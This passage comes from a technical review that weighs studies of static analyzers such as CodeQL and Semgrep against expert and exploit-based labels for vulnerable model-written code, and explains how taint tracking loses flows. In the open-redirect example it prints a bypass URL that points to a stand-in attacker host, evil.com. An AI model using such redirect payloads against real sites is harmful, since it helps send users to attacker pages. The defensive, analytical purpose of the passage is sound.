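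The last kind of oracle is another language model. A model can judge thousands of programs, but someone has to validate it first. The judge that Lunghi and colleagues used agreed with one of their engineers on 74% of the 50 programs and with the other on 72%. Where the two engineers agreed with each other, it matched them on 85% of programs. Other judges have done much worse. Dai, Xu and Tao (2026) tried two open-weight models in *Rethinking the Evaluation of Secure Code Generation* and checked a sample by hand. By the counts in the paper's 2025 version, 21 of 42 programs were vulnerable, but Llama 3.3 70B flagged all 42 and Qwen2.5 72B flagged 38. In one case Qwen reported a leak through logging in code that did no logging.

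These oracles aren't interchangeable. *The Illusion of Safety* (Mahmud, Sikder and colleagues, 2026) compared two of them on 4,962 C++ programs written by language models and people. It used a pair of sanitizers, which check a running program for memory and arithmetic errors, and a bounded model checker, which covers all inputs but follows loops only up to a limit. The sanitizers flagged 657 programs and the model checker flagged 1,280, but both flagged only 120 of the same programs. In the wider benchmark, the models' code did worse than human code under the sanitizers and better under the model checker. The results differ partly because sanitizers check only what the tests execute, while the model checker may consider inputs that a real user would never supply. Measured recall therefore always depends on what the chosen oracle counts as insecure.

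### CodeQL and Semgrep against expert labels

Firouzi and Ghafari took their programs from *Benchmarking Prompt Engineering Techniques for Secure Code Generation with GPT Models* (2025) by Bruni, Gabrielli and colleagues, who had already scanned them with CodeQL and Semgrep. GPT-4o, now an old model, wrote ten Python programs for each of 108 tasks, criticizing and revising its own work. Each task targets one of the 25 types of weakness that MITRE lists as most dangerous.

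The reviewers found the target weakness in 39% of the programs. Measured against their labels, CodeQL had a precision of 0.67 and a recall of 0.34, and Semgrep had a precision of 0.52 and a recall of 0.54. When only programs flagged by both tools counted, precision rose to 0.76 and recall fell to 0.30.

These figures are enough to rebuild the approximate counts. About 421 of the 1,080 programs were vulnerable. CodeQL caught 34% of them, or 143, and since those make up 67% of its flags, it flagged about 214 programs in all. The same steps give the other rows:

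| | Vulnerable, flagged | Vulnerable, missed | Secure, flagged | Secure, not flagged | Agreement with labels |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| CodeQL | 143 | 278 | 71 | 588 | 68% |
| Semgrep | 227 | 194 | 210 | 449 | 63% |
| Both tools | 126 | 295 | 40 | 619 | 69% |

The last column conflicts with the paper's text, which gives 61% agreement for CodeQL and 65% for Semgrep. Rounding can't explain the difference. With 61% agreement, CodeQL's precision would be about 0.50 and its recall about 0.26, and Semgrep would be better on both measures. The precision and recall in the results table imply that CodeQL passed 80% of the programs and Semgrep 60%, which matches the totals in the text, so the calculations here use the results table.

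Agreement with the labels is a poor measure because 61% of the programs were secure. A tool that never raised an alert would have agreed 61% of the time, only two points less than Semgrep. The overall share of programs that a tool passes can also mislead. Semgrep passed 60% of them, almost exactly the share that were secure, but it missed 194 vulnerable programs and flagged 210 secure ones.

A clean scan is weak evidence of safety here. Overall, 39% of the programs contained their target weakness. Among the 866 that CodeQL did not flag, 278 (32%) contained it. Among those that Semgrep did not flag, 30% did.

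The precision figures could be too low. Both tools often reported weaknesses other than the target, and nobody checked those reports. Where those reports counted as flags, some apparent false alarms may be real weaknesses of another type. The sample is also effectively smaller than it looks, because ten attempts at the same task tend to contain the same mistake, and a query that misses it in one attempt may miss it in all ten.

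### Whether a flag is better than a guess

Lift is a tool's precision divided by the base rate, the share of all programs that are insecure. A lift of 1 means that a flagged program is no more likely to be insecure than one picked at random. A precision of 67% is therefore useful if 39% of programs are insecure but worthless if 67% are. In Firouzi and Ghafari's data, the lift is about 1.7 for CodeQL, 1.3 for Semgrep and 1.9 when both tools flag a program.

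Lunghi and colleagues found almost no lift on three Python benchmarks. Their oracle was a set of security tests on SecEvalPlus, live exploits on BaxBench and the validated model judge on RiskyPy. The static tools were Bandit and Semgrep's `p/security-audit` rules. They left out CodeQL because it is too slow to run after every generated line, as their experiment required. The table covers only programs that worked, and a program counts as flagged if either tool raised an alert.

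| Benchmark and model | Programs | Insecure | Flagged | Precision | Recall | Lift |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| SecEvalPlus, Qwen2.5-Coder-14B | 102 | 87.3% | 5.9% | 83.3% | 5.6% | 0.95 |
| SecEvalPlus, DeepSeek-V4.1-flash | 347 | 62.0% | 3.5% | 75.0% | 4.2% | 1.21 |
| SecEvalPlus, Qwen2.5-72B | 280 | 81.1% | 5.4% | 80.0% | 5.3% | 0.99 |
| BaxBench, Qwen2.5-Coder-14B | 12 | 66.7% | 83.3% | 70.0% | 87.5% | 1.05 |
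| BaxBench, DeepSeek-V4.1-flash | 166 | 41.0% | 34.3% | 38.6% | 32.4% | 0.94 |
| BaxBench, Qwen2.5-72B | 67 | 61.2% | 37.3% | 68.0% | 41.5% | 1.11 |
| RiskyPy, Qwen2.5-Coder-14B | 53 | 56.6% | 75.5% | 60.0% | 80.0% | 1.06 |
| RiskyPy, DeepSeek-V4.1-flash | 211 | 45.5% | 89.6% | 47.6% | 93.8% | 1.05 |
| RiskyPy, Qwen2.5-72B | 181 | 58.0% | 76.8% | 61.2% | 81.0% | 1.06 |

The three benchmarks have low lift for different reasons. On SecEvalPlus the tools rarely raised an alert, so the three precision figures rest on about 6, 12 and 15 flagged programs. The base rate also limits lift. When 87% of programs are insecure, even perfect precision gives a lift of only 1.15. Recall is the more informative number for this benchmark, and it is very low.

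The most frequent alert on BaxBench flags the required network setting, so it can't separate exploitable applications from the rest. DeepSeek's flagged applications were slightly less likely to be exploitable than its applications overall.

The tools' high recall on RiskyPy is misleading. It was almost guaranteed, because RiskyPy includes a task only if Bandit or Semgrep had flagged a trial solution. The counts for DeepSeek imply that the tools flagged 94% of its insecure programs and about 86% of its secure ones. Errors by the model judge may have lowered the lift further, since random labelling mistakes pull it towards 1.

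Lunghi and colleagues conclude that the flags are barely more likely than chance to mark insecure code. That is fair for these rules on these tasks, but it provides little evidence about taint analysis. Only 11 of the 225 Semgrep rules ever interrupted generation in their experiments. The most frequently triggered rules flag code such as a call to `eval`, Python's standard XML parser or a subprocess that uses the shell. Such code is often dangerous, but the rules flag it whether or not an attacker's data can reach it.

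### Insecure code that passed the scan

Some researchers have started from the opposite end, with code that analyzers passed, and looked for what they had missed.

Dai and colleagues tested four techniques meant to make models write safer code through extra training, changes to how the model picks each word, or rewritten prompts. CodeQL rated nearly all the code secure, including code from models without these techniques. On BigCodeBench, a general set of Python tasks, it passed 99% of the solutions GPT-4o wrote without them, while the analyzers Bearer and Bandit passed 64% and 75%. Starting from 99%, a technique has almost no room to raise CodeQL's pass rate, even if it makes the code safer.

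Mistral 7B wrote the hand-checked programs after being trained with one of the techniques. Of the 21 vulnerable programs, CodeQL found 2, Bearer 9 and Bandit 3. CodeQL raised no false alarms, Bearer raised 6 and Bandit 2. The paper describes a sample of 44, but the counts for each tool add up to 42. CodeQL's recall of 2 in 21 (about 10%) is far below the 34% in Firouzi and Ghafari's study, although with so few programs the true figure could easily be two or three times as high.

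A clean result sometimes meant that little code was left. In one case, a technique deleted the whole body of a function and kept only its imports and first line. Dai and colleagues also inspected DeepSeek-Coder solutions that stopped working when a technique made them "secure". Deleted code caused 60% to 92% of these failures, depending on the technique.

Blain and Noiseux report the highest miss rate. They generated 250 programs in C and Python from 50 prompts, and Z3 proved a flaw in 90 of them. Six tools, including Semgrep, Bandit and CodeQL, missed 88 of the 90, or 97.8%. The two hits were coincidental, because Semgrep had flagged a risky string function in the same code, not the overflow that Z3 had proved. CodeQL's `security-extended` suite found none of the 90.

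They attribute CodeQL's result to integer overflow in memory allocation, as in the `malloc` example. This is a good explanation for that flaw, because taint analysis can follow `n` from a file to the call, but the overflow depends on how large `n` can get, which a data flow graph does not record. The explanation can't apply to the 22 Python programs among the 90, because Python's integers grow as needed instead of wrapping around. The design also favours the solver, because the comparison with CodeQL included only flaws that COBALT had already proved. It therefore omits any flaw COBALT missed and gives no precision for CodeQL.

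In *Beyond Static Guarantees*, Pourleyli, Urmi and Melo (2026) tried to exploit Python code that had passed both Bandit and Semgrep. They began with 1,355 samples from three security datasets, of which 654 produced no alerts. An agent built on GPT-5.4 nano, a small language model, read these 654 samples and named suspected weaknesses. A second agent built on the same model wrote attacks and ran them in an isolated container. Each agent made five attempts, and a result counted only if at least three agreed. The attacks succeeded against 83 of the 654 samples (12.7%) and partly succeeded against another 12.

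The 12.7% does not measure recall, because the agents never tested the flagged files and attacked only weaknesses that the first agent had suspected. Nor does it estimate the rate for everyday generated code, since 106 of the 120 confirmed weaknesses came from RedCode, a collection of deliberately risky code, and only 2 came from SecurityEval, whose tasks are closest to ordinary programming requests. The same model was also used to suspect and to confirm flaws, so it could make the same mistake at both steps. It confirmed all 29 suspected cases of weak random numbers, possibly because the "attack" only had to show that the program used an ordinary random number generator.

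### Why the results range from 0% to 94%

Put side by side, the results seem to describe different tools:

| Study | Tool and rules | Code | Precision | Recall |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Firouzi and Ghafari | CodeQL | GPT-4o, tasks built around CWEs | 67% | 34% |
| Firouzi and Ghafari | Semgrep | The same | 52% | 54% |
| Dai and colleagues | CodeQL | Functions from a hardened Mistral 7B | 2 of 2 | 2 of 21 |
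| Blain and Noiseux | CodeQL, `security-extended` | Programs with a solver-proven flaw | Not measured | 0 of 90 |
| Lunghi and colleagues | Semgrep `p/security-audit` and Bandit | Three Python benchmarks | 39–83% | 4–94% |

*Understanding and Improving Model Editing for Secure Code Generation* (2026) compared CodeQL's results with a manual inspection of 40 generated programs and found that CodeQL was right about 37. It raised one false alarm, on code that wrote a short number into a buffer with plenty of room, and missed two real flaws. Its precision was 95% and its recall 90.5%, which further widens the range of results for CodeQL.

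That result shows how much depends on the rules. The researchers ran 29 official queries and 12 that the makers of earlier benchmarks had written for these scenarios. Someone had also inspected the queries on the original benchmark and reported two errors, which the CodeQL team fixed. Because the queries were fitted to the test, the result doesn't show how well CodeQL performs off the shelf.

The sample's recall is also too high for the full set of programs, because half of the 40 sampled programs were flagged, while CodeQL flagged only 21% to 37% of the code from the unmodified models. If we assume a flagged share of 30% and use the sample's vulnerability rates of 95% for flagged programs and 10% for unflagged ones, recall is about 80%. This estimate is rough because the 10% comes from two programs out of 20.

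Recall depends as much on how researchers chose the tasks as on which rules they ran. The same Semgrep rules and Bandit caught at least 80% of the insecure programs on RiskyPy, where every task had already triggered an alert, and about 5% on SecEvalPlus, where many weaknesses have no recognizable pattern. Neither rate would predict recall on a company's own code.

A study's set-up can also affect its results more than other factors do. In *Cross-Cutting Security Analysis of LLM-Generated Code*, Peng, Wang and Zhu (2026) generated 3,700 programs from LLMSecEval, the prompt collection that supplied some of Firouzi and Ghafari's tasks. CodeQL flagged 3 of the programs, or 0.1%, compared with about 20% in Firouzi and Ghafari's sample. Semgrep flagged 2.4%. The difference in models hardly explains so large a gap, and other researchers have had many CodeQL findings on closely related prompts. The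 gap probably comes from the procedure. Peng and colleagues counted only alerts that mapped to nine kinds of weakness, and nearly half of the programs were in C, which CodeQL normally analyses during a successful build. Their 68.8% vulnerability rate also needs caution, because it comes from a Claude model's verdicts, which were reviewed by hand for only 36 programs.

### Lost flows and weaknesses that are not flows

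Low recall alone doesn't show that taint tracking fails on generated code, because many of the missed weaknesses involve no flow of untrusted data for it to track.

Missing authorization is the clearest case of a weakness that involves no data flow. Peng and colleagues' model judge reported it in 536 programs, and none of their four static tools flagged any. Even if the judge was often wrong, the tools would be expected to miss this kind of weakness. Weak random numbers and badly hashed passwords also make code insecure without an attacker's input having to reach the wrong function, but a rule can catch them by recognizing that function.

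Of the 120 confirmed weaknesses in Pourleyli and colleagues' results, at least 44 were weak random numbers, poor password hashing or missing authorization. Only 13 were in the two listed categories that concern file paths an outsider can influence, which taint analysis is routinely used to find. Bandit and Semgrep raised no alerts anywhere in the collection for several categories, including poor password hashing and missing authorization, and better taint tracking would not have helped with those.

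Other misses have a dangerous sink but no recognized source. Dai and colleagues show a function that runs a shell script supplied by its caller. CodeQL's default and extended rules for command injection reported nothing, probably because the benchmark asked for individual functions, so the code contains no web request, and CodeQL's standard settings do not treat ordinary function arguments as untrusted. Dai and colleagues call the function vulnerable because a caller could pass in a malicious script, while CodeQL's designers assume that the caller is part of the same trusted program. Both positions are reasonable, since the same code can be exploitable or harmless depending on where a developer pastes it.

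In the remaining cases, the weakness is a complete flow from source to sink, so a miss counts against taint analysis itself. Firouzi and Ghafari give the example of a web page that redirects visitors to an address taken from the request. GPT-4o had added a check that the address belonged to `example.com`, but an address such as `https://example.com@evil.com` may pass the check and lead to `evil.com`. Neither tool raised an alert. The tools may have treated the faulty check as a sanitizer or lost track of the data before the redirect.

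CodeQL's 34% recall mixes all of these cases. It fairly estimates how much a team would catch by running the tool on similar code, but it doesn't measure how often CodeQL misses a flow that one of its queries covers. If many of the misses were not flows, that rate must be lower than the overall miss rate of 66%, but these totals aren't enough to calculate how much lower.

### What the tools are still good for

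The strongest argument for static analysis is that it takes little time and computation. Bandit and Semgrep needed 77 seconds to scan all of Pourleyli and colleagues' 1,355 files. The two model-based stages then took more than 28 hours and 96 million tokens to examine the remaining 654. Since a scan can quickly pick out some of the vulnerable programs, it makes sense to scan first and run attacks only on the rest.

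A lightweight first filter only has to be right about the programs it flags. CodeQL comes closer to this than Semgrep, with 71 false alarms to Semgrep's 210 on Firouzi and Ghafari's programs. The programs CodeQL passes should still go through later checks, since about a third of them were vulnerable. Model judges tend to miss few vulnerable programs but flag many safe ones. In Dai and colleagues' sample, Qwen flagged 20 of the 21 vulnerable programs and 18 of the 21 safe ones. A scanner and a judge may therefore be more useful together than either is alone.

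Using two analyzers helps even more with precision. CodeQL and Semgrep flagged about 166 of the same programs in Firouzi and Ghafari's sample, and 126 of those were vulnerable. A random selection of 166 programs would have included about 65 vulnerable ones. Subtracting the shared flags from Semgrep's total leaves about 271 programs that only Semgrep flagged, and 37% of these were vulnerable, slightly below the base rate. The share was no higher among the roughly 48 programs that only CodeQL flagged. A team with limited time should start with the programs that both tools flag, although precision will be lower wherever vulnerable programs are rarer than in this sample.

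Agreement between two tools is stronger evidence when they work differently, as CodeQL's taint queries and Semgrep's search rules do. Agreement between Semgrep and Bandit is weaker evidence. Lunghi and colleagues note that these two tools share rules for the most common patterns in their benchmarks, including `eval` and Python's `pickle` format. Where the rules are the same, the tools will agree even when both are wrong.

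## Where flows are lost in Python and JavaScript

The 34% recall that Firouzi and Ghafari measured for CodeQL is not specific to flows. *PyFlow* (Gu, Yan and Yao, 2026) comes closer to measuring how often CodeQL misses them. It compares analyzers on 108 published vulnerabilities from 62 open-source Python projects, all of six types in which untrusted data reaches a dangerous operation, such as SQL injection and path traversal. CodeQL found 31.8% of them, so it misses most such flows in real Python code too. Some of the causes are in the languages, and others are choices tool makers made to limit false alarms.

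### Two names for one object

The program below reads a secret from an environment variable and passes it to a function called `send`:

```python
1  settings = {}
2  report = settings
3  settings["token"] = os.environ["API_TOKEN"]
4  send(report["token"])
```

Line 2 gives the dictionary a second name instead of copying it, so line 4 uses `report` to read the value that line 3 stores through `settings`. Two expressions are aliases at a point in a program if both can refer to the same object when execution reaches that point.

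An analyzer that records taint by variable name marks `settings` as tainted on line 3. Nothing assigns a new value to `report` after that, so the analyzer still treats `report` as clean on line 4 and misses the flow. If lines 2 and 3 are swapped, the analyzer finds the flow because `report = settings` then copies the taint. If the lines stay in their original order but line 2 is `report = settings.copy()`, the names refer to two separate dictionaries and the secret never reaches `send`.

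To tell these versions apart, an analyzer needs a points-to analysis, which works out which objects each variable may refer to. This analysis usually labels an object by the line that creates it, so here both names point to "the dictionary from line 1". The analyzer can then attach the taint to that dictionary's `token` entry and find it under either name. Gu and colleagues' analyzer, PyFlow, works this way.

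The labels are approximate. If a loop creates a thousand dictionaries on one line, they all share one label, so a secret stored in one appears to be in all of them.

Missing alias information can also cause false alarms. Suppose the program stores the secret through `report` and then overwrites it with an empty string through `settings`. The secret is gone, but an analyzer that treats the names as separate objects still marks `report["token"]` as tainted. A cautious analyzer adds taint to both names if they might refer to the same object, but it can safely remove taint from both only if they definitely do.

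### Flow, field and context sensitivity

A flow-sensitive analysis takes the order of statements into account. If a program puts a secret in `key`, replaces it with the word "none" and then sends `key`, a flow-sensitive analyzer reports nothing. An analyzer without flow sensitivity records only that `key` held a secret somewhere in the function, so it raises a false alarm. The drawback is that a flow-sensitive analyzer has to keep separate facts for each point in the program.

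A field-sensitive analysis distinguishes the parts of an object, so a secret in `settings["token"]` does not taint `settings["colour"]`. It has to track every part separately, including nested parts such as `user.account.keys[0]`. It also needs the points-to analysis to identify which object each field belongs to.

A context-sensitive analysis distinguishes different calls to the same function. If a program calls both `tidy(secret)` and `tidy("hello")`, an analysis without context sensitivity merges the two calls and treats both results as tainted. The simplest remedy is to analyze `tidy` again for every chain of calls that leads to it, but the number of chains can grow exponentially with the depth of the call graph.

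PyFlow uses IFDS, a method that needs less computation. It builds a graph whose nodes pair a place in the program with a fact, such as "line 8, `key` is tainted". The fact can hold at that place if the graph contains a valid path to the node. Once the solver finds that taint entering `tidy` through its argument leaves through its return value, it saves this as a summary and reuses it at every other call to `tidy`.

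PyFlow's analysis takes a lot of computation. A single Python statement such as `obj.attr[key].method(args)` turns into five or more operations. Splitting code this finely gives PyFlow three to five times as many nodes as it would have if each node were a block of statements. Gu and colleagues allowed ten minutes for each of 206 program versions, and 45 of them ran out of time. The median solving time for the 159 that finished was 6.8 seconds, so most programs are quick to analyze and a minority take very long.

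Each timeout counted as a program with no detections. An analysis that is too precise to finish in time therefore has lower recall, because it misses every flow in that program.

### Calls whose target is not in the text

The analyzer records which functions may call which others as edges in a call graph, and it follows these edges to track taint from one function to another. If an edge is missing, taint tracking stops at that call, however well the analyzer handles the code on either side.

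In Python and JavaScript, the text of a call often doesn't identify the function that will run. asciinema, a Python program that records terminal sessions, chooses its commands roughly like this:

```python
parser.set_defaults(cmd=RecordCommand)
args = parser.parse_args()
command = args.cmd(args)
command.execute()
```

The first line passes a class to Python's standard command-line parser, which later stores it in `args.cmd`. The third line calls whatever is stored there. To find the call's target, an analyzer has to model how the parser copies defaults onto `args`, track the class as data, and work out which `execute` method the resulting object has.

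Zięba-Kozarzewski and Grzegorzewski (2026), in *When Static Reachability Says No*, measured how such code affects Joern, an open-source analyzer that, like CodeQL, turns programs into queryable graphs. Starting from asciinema's entry points, their query on Joern's graph reached 11 of 134 functions. When they ran the program, 113 of the 123 supposedly unreachable functions executed. In a second program, Sublist3r, 19 of 24 supposedly unreachable functions executed. Semgrep's security rules had raised six alerts in these programs. Five were in code that was unreachable according to Joern's graph, but the code behind all five ran.

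Adding four missing edges to asciinema's graph made 50 of the 113 functions reachable, while reaching all 113 took 50 edges. Three of the four belong to the command selection shown above, and the fourth is a call to a function that is a parameter's default value. The study covers only two small programs, chosen because Joern's results differed from a hand-built call graph, so its rates don't describe Python code in general. But command-line tools routinely select commands the way asciinema does.

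Some Python syntax calls functions implicitly. A `with` block runs one method when it begins and another when it ends, and reading `user.name` runs a function if the class defines `name` as a property. These two forms accounted for 29 of the 73 edges missing from asciinema's call graph.

Callbacks and decorators hide the caller. Nothing in the ten-line Flask program calls `show_user`. The decorator `@app.route("/user")` gives the function to Flask, which calls it when a request arrives.

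When types are missing, the variable `n` in `n.notify()` could hold an object of any class that has a `notify` method. Joern sometimes links such a call to every method with the right name, which avoids missing a real edge but adds false edges to methods of classes that the program never passes in.

Python programs can also add or replace attributes whose names are computed at run time. PyFlow missed some flows in its own evaluation because the code it analyzed set attributes with `setattr`, which takes the attribute's name as a string.

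JavaScript programmers use computed names even more freely, because a JavaScript object is essentially a dictionary whose entries the program can change at any time. Express, a popular framework for web servers, builds part of its interface in a loop. In simplified form:

```js
const app = {};
for (const method of ["get", "post", "put"]) {
  app[method] = function (path, handler) { /* register the handler */ };
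}
app.get("/user", showUser);
```

No line assigns anything to `app.get` by that name. Laursen, Xu and Møller (2024), in *Reducing Static Analysis Unsoundness with Approximate Interpretation*, use the real Express code to show the two usual ways of handling such an assignment. An analyzer can ignore it, but then it finds no target for the call to `app.get` and misses any aliases the assignment created. Or it can assume that the function could be assigned to any property of `app`, so that every method call on `app` could run any of these functions. On an object with 30 methods, one call would have 30 possible targets, and two calls in a row would have 900 combinations. Laursen and colleagues report that analyzers built on this assumption become too imprecise and slow for large programs, which is why others ignore the assignments.

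### How much of the call graph is missing

*PyCG* (Salis, Sotiropoulos and colleagues, 2021) presents one of the best-known call-graph tools for Python. On real projects, about 99% of the edges the tool reported were correct, and it found about 70% of the edges in hand-built graphs. The 70% figure may overstate its recall, because the hand-built graphs are incomplete. When Zięba-Kozarzewski and Grzegorzewski ran Sublist3r, 21 of the 87 direct calls they observed were missing from its hand-built graph.

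A reference call graph recorded by running the programs doesn't depend on anyone reading the code correctly, but it covers only the code that runs. Bouzenia, Krishan and Pradel (2024), in *DyPyBench*, recorded calls during the test suites of 39 Python projects and found only 49% of the observed edges in PyCG's graphs. This figure probably overstates the problem for taint analysis. Methods of built-in types, such as the `strip` on line 7 of the Flask program, made up 59% of the called functions missing from PyCG's graphs. A taint analyzer doesn't need an edge into `strip` if it has a library model for it. Roughly another 12% of the mismatches arose only because the two tools named the same function differently.

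PyCG does much better on code written to test it. In the comparison in *CPyGraph* (2026), PyCG missed no edge in 103 of 112 tiny Python programs. Each program exercises a language feature in a few lines, so the gap between this result and the 49% shows that a tool's support for individual features predicts little about its performance on whole projects.

Newer tools have improved on PyCG only modestly. Huang, Yan and colleagues (2023) tested a flow-sensitive tool called JARVIS in *Scalable and Precise Application-Centered Call Graph Construction for Python*. When they counted only calls in chains that start at an application's entry functions, JARVIS had a recall of 0.66 and PyCG had 0.61.

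For JavaScript, Laursen and colleagues measured recall against the calls made when running the test suites of 36 projects. Their static analyzer, which ignored computed property names, found 75.9% of these calls on average. They then added a step that runs parts of the code in advance and records which functions are assigned to which properties. This works for libraries like Express because they initialize the same way every time. Average recall rose to 88.1%, and in one project it rose from 40.1% to 98.0%. Precision fell by 1.5%.

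| Tool | Code | Reference | Share of calls found |
|---|---|---|---|
| PyCG | Python projects | Hand-built call graphs | 70% |
| PyCG | 39 Python projects | Calls observed in tests | 49% |
| PyCG | Python applications, from entry functions | Test traces and manual inspection | 61% |
| JARVIS | The same | The same | 66% |
| Laursen and colleagues' analyzer | 36 JavaScript projects | Calls observed in tests | 76% |
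| The same, with the advance run | The same | The same | 88% |

An analyzer can follow a flow across several functions only if it has every edge on the route. If it has 76% of the edges and the gaps fall at random, it can follow about 44% of the flows that cross three calls. With 88% of the edges, it can follow about 68%. As asciinema shows, real gaps instead cluster at the few places where a program selects what to run next, so one program may lose nearly all its flows and another hardly any.

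None of these figures measures CodeQL's or Semgrep's own call graph. They show how hard the problem is for tools that do little else.

### What CodeQL and Semgrep follow

CodeQL's JavaScript engine covers most ordinary language features. *Preserve the Vulnerability, Break the Alert* (Cao, Ding and Xu, 2026) reports that these include closures, which are functions that keep access to the variables around them.

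Gu and colleagues describe CodeQL's tracking for Python as a search through a graph in which each assignment to a variable creates a new version of it. This lets the analyzer distinguish `key` when it held a secret from `key` after a later line overwrote it. But these versions don't identify all the other names for an object that has changed. GitHub acknowledges in its documentation that aliases and call targets determined at run time cause trouble for CodeQL too.

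Semgrep tracks less than CodeQL does. Gu and colleagues list it as having only limited tracking between functions and no points-to analysis. Without points-to analysis, it has no general way to connect `settings` with `report`. Their description fits the free edition. The paid edition restores many call edges, but calls whose target is chosen at run time remain difficult in both editions.

Semgrep avoids some of these losses by passing taint through calls to unknown functions by default. That doesn't help if the function stores the data in an object or passes it to another function instead of returning it.

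### Missing library models and the price of guessing

An analyzer that relies on library models, as CodeQL does, would still lose flows at unmodelled library calls even if its call graph for the project's own code were perfect. It may correctly identify which library function the program calls but have no model of what that function does with its input.

Fixing a missing edge inside a project usually requires a better analysis, while fixing a missing library model requires someone to write a few lines describing the function. Models can also make hard analysis unnecessary. For example, a model of Express can mark the handler passed to `app.get` as a function that receives web requests, so the tool doesn't have to analyze the loop that created `app.get`.

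Because writing models for every package is impractical, Semgrep by default treats the result of an unfamiliar call as tainted if any of its arguments are. This causes false alerts, since many calls don't pass on what they receive. For example, a function that checks a password may return only `True` or `False`, and logging that result doesn't reveal the password. Taint also spreads from each result to the values computed from it, so eventually many harmless log lines and requests get flagged.

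An analysis is sound if it never misses a behavior that could occur. In practice, analyzers can only approach soundness on real Python and JavaScript programs by including many behaviors that can't occur, so their makers deliberately give up soundness to keep precision and speed. Samhi, Just and colleagues (2024) found the same trade-off in *Call Graph Soundness in Android Static Analysis*. They ran 13 tools on 1,000 Android apps, and on average the tools missed 61% of the methods that the apps executed. Call graphs with high precision tended to miss many methods.

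Unsound tools can also be imprecise. In the most demanding of Huang and colleagues' settings, PyCG's precision fell to 0.19, so about four in five of the edges it reported were wrong. JARVIS reached 0.35, mainly because it takes the order of statements into account. A taint analyzer using either graph would follow many paths that don't exist, and its false alarms would multiply with each further call.

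CodeQL favors precision over recall, so the flows it reports are usually correct. *In Specs we Trust?* (2025) used a CodeQL query to trace information through packages for Node-RED, a visual tool for connecting devices and online services. A check of all 964 flows that the query reported in 97 packages found that 951 were correct. The paper didn't measure how many flows the query missed, because searching the packages by hand would have taken too much work. A JavaScript flow that a well-made query reports is thus very likely to exist, but the absence of a report is much weaker evidence that there is no flow.

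### Known vulnerabilities in real projects

Published vulnerabilities offer a fairer test than call graphs, since what counts is whether the analyzer raises the right alert. Researchers run it on the vulnerable version, where it should report the flaw, and on the repaired version, where it should not. The benchmark of 108 Python vulnerabilities comes from Liu, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *An Empirical Study on Static Application Security Testing (SAST) Tools for Python*. Gu and colleagues reused it, along with the earlier study's set of 120 vulnerable programs written by DeepSeek-V3, a language model:

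| Tool | Precision, real projects | Recall, real projects | Precision, DeepSeek programs | Recall, DeepSeek programs |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| CodeQL | 72.3% | 31.8% | 84.5% | 40.8% |
| Semgrep | 65.7% | 40.7% | 83.2% | 65.8% |
| Bandit | 60.0% | 27.8% | 70.6% | 40.0% |
| Snyk | 80.0% | 11.9% | 91.2% | 70.5% |
| PyFlow | 71.2% | 48.1% | 83.7% | 85.8% |

Semgrep found more of the real vulnerabilities than CodeQL, although its taint analysis is weaker. This is probably because most of its public rules are search rules, which need no source, so its 40.7% doesn't measure taint tracking. In the precision figures, a report on the repaired version counted as a false alarm, but alerts elsewhere in the project did not count, so a developer scanning the whole project could see a very different share of false alarms.

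PyFlow's higher recall, despite its timeouts, suggests that points-to information and context sensitivity help, but it still missed more than half of the real vulnerabilities. Liu and colleagues found that even all eight of the analyzers they tested, combined, detected only 66.7% of vulnerabilities.

A second comparison had similar results for CodeQL. In *Finding Vulnerabilities via LLM-Augmented Semantics-Aware Type-Checking* (2026), CodeQL's default Python queries had a recall of 0.39 on 80 real vulnerabilities and 0.22 on a small set of recent ones, with a precision of 0.67 on both. The scores for the recent set are consistent with CodeQL catching 2 out of 9 vulnerabilities, so the lower recall is weak evidence that CodeQL does worse on recent vulnerabilities.

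The test sets for Node.js, which runs JavaScript outside the browser, are outdated. Afonso, Pereira and colleagues (2026) point out in *X.js* that the two most commonly used collections of flow vulnerabilities contain nothing later than 2022. The median vulnerable package had about 250 lines of code in 2021 and 2022 and 6,100 in 2026. An analysis has few places to lose a flow in 250 lines, so success on the old collections is probably weak evidence of how well a tool handles the packages in which people now find vulnerabilities. Their new collection has 1,159 working exploits for 965 packages and records where the data enters and where it does harm, which should make lost flows much easier to study.

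CodeQL's lowest score comes from Java. *QLCoder* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2025) tested it on 176 published vulnerabilities in 111 Java projects, and its general queries had an F1 score of 0.073. F1 combines precision and recall into one number, which is low if either is low. If CodeQL's recall was about one third, as in the Python studies, its precision would have been about 4%.

Wang and colleagues also had a language model write a separate CodeQL query for each vulnerability, and these queries scored 0.7. The model had the public description of the flaw and the code of the repair. It could run each draft on the vulnerable and repaired versions of the project and revise it up to ten times. The general queries were written without this help, and their alerts about other real flaws in the same project may have been counted as mistakes. The comparison is therefore unfair to the general queries,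 but it is still informative about CodeQL's engine, which was the same in both cases.

In one of the projects, a web request reaches an XML parser that an attacker can cause to open external files. The successful query named the request as the source and the parser as the sink, added propagation steps for the way the program builds its parser, and listed the setting that makes the parser safe. Wang and colleagues note that gaps in CodeQL's data flow often need such extra steps. For 53.4% of the vulnerabilities, the purpose-written queries raised an alert on the vulnerable code and none on the repaired code. In many cases, then, CodeQL can follow the flow once a query specifies the source, the sink and any missing steps. For the other 46.6%, even a model that had the answer failed to produce a working query, though the cause may be the model rather than CodeQL.

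### Whether model-written code is easier to follow

Short programs from a language model are likely to suit these tools because they often fit in one file, which removes the calls between modules. They also tend to use popular libraries, which are the most likely to have library models.

The DeepSeek programs are the best available test. Each has at least 80 lines, is self-contained and has exactly one source and one sink. Every tool in the table had higher recall on them than on the real projects, and Snyk's was nearly six times as high. CodeQL had the smallest proportional gain on the simpler code, from 31.8% to 40.8%.

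Short, self-contained code is easier to analyze, but it doesn't remove CodeQL's main difficulty. Calls between files can't explain misses in such programs, so the more likely causes are gaps in library models and in the shipped queries' lists of sources and sinks. PyFlow's misses on these programs also suggest this. Gu and colleagues traced its 17 failures to library code with incomplete descriptions and to attribute names computed at runtime.

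The researchers had DeepSeek put a known vulnerability into each program, with 20 programs for each of the six types, so the programs aren't a sample of what people ask models to write. The advantage of short code also disappears when a model writes a whole application, since it will then use the same decorators, callbacks and command tables as human programmers. DeepSeek's programs differ from real projects in author, length and type of program, so comparing them can't show whether models' code is harder to follow than people's. To find that out, researchers would have to give models and people the same tasks and count the lost flows in each.

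Whether CodeQL finds a flow can also depend on how the program is written. Cao and colleagues found that after a language model rewrote code in ordinary-looking ways, CodeQL missed 26.2% of 172 real flows it had previously detected, although the vulnerabilities were still there.

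## Secrets sent to the network

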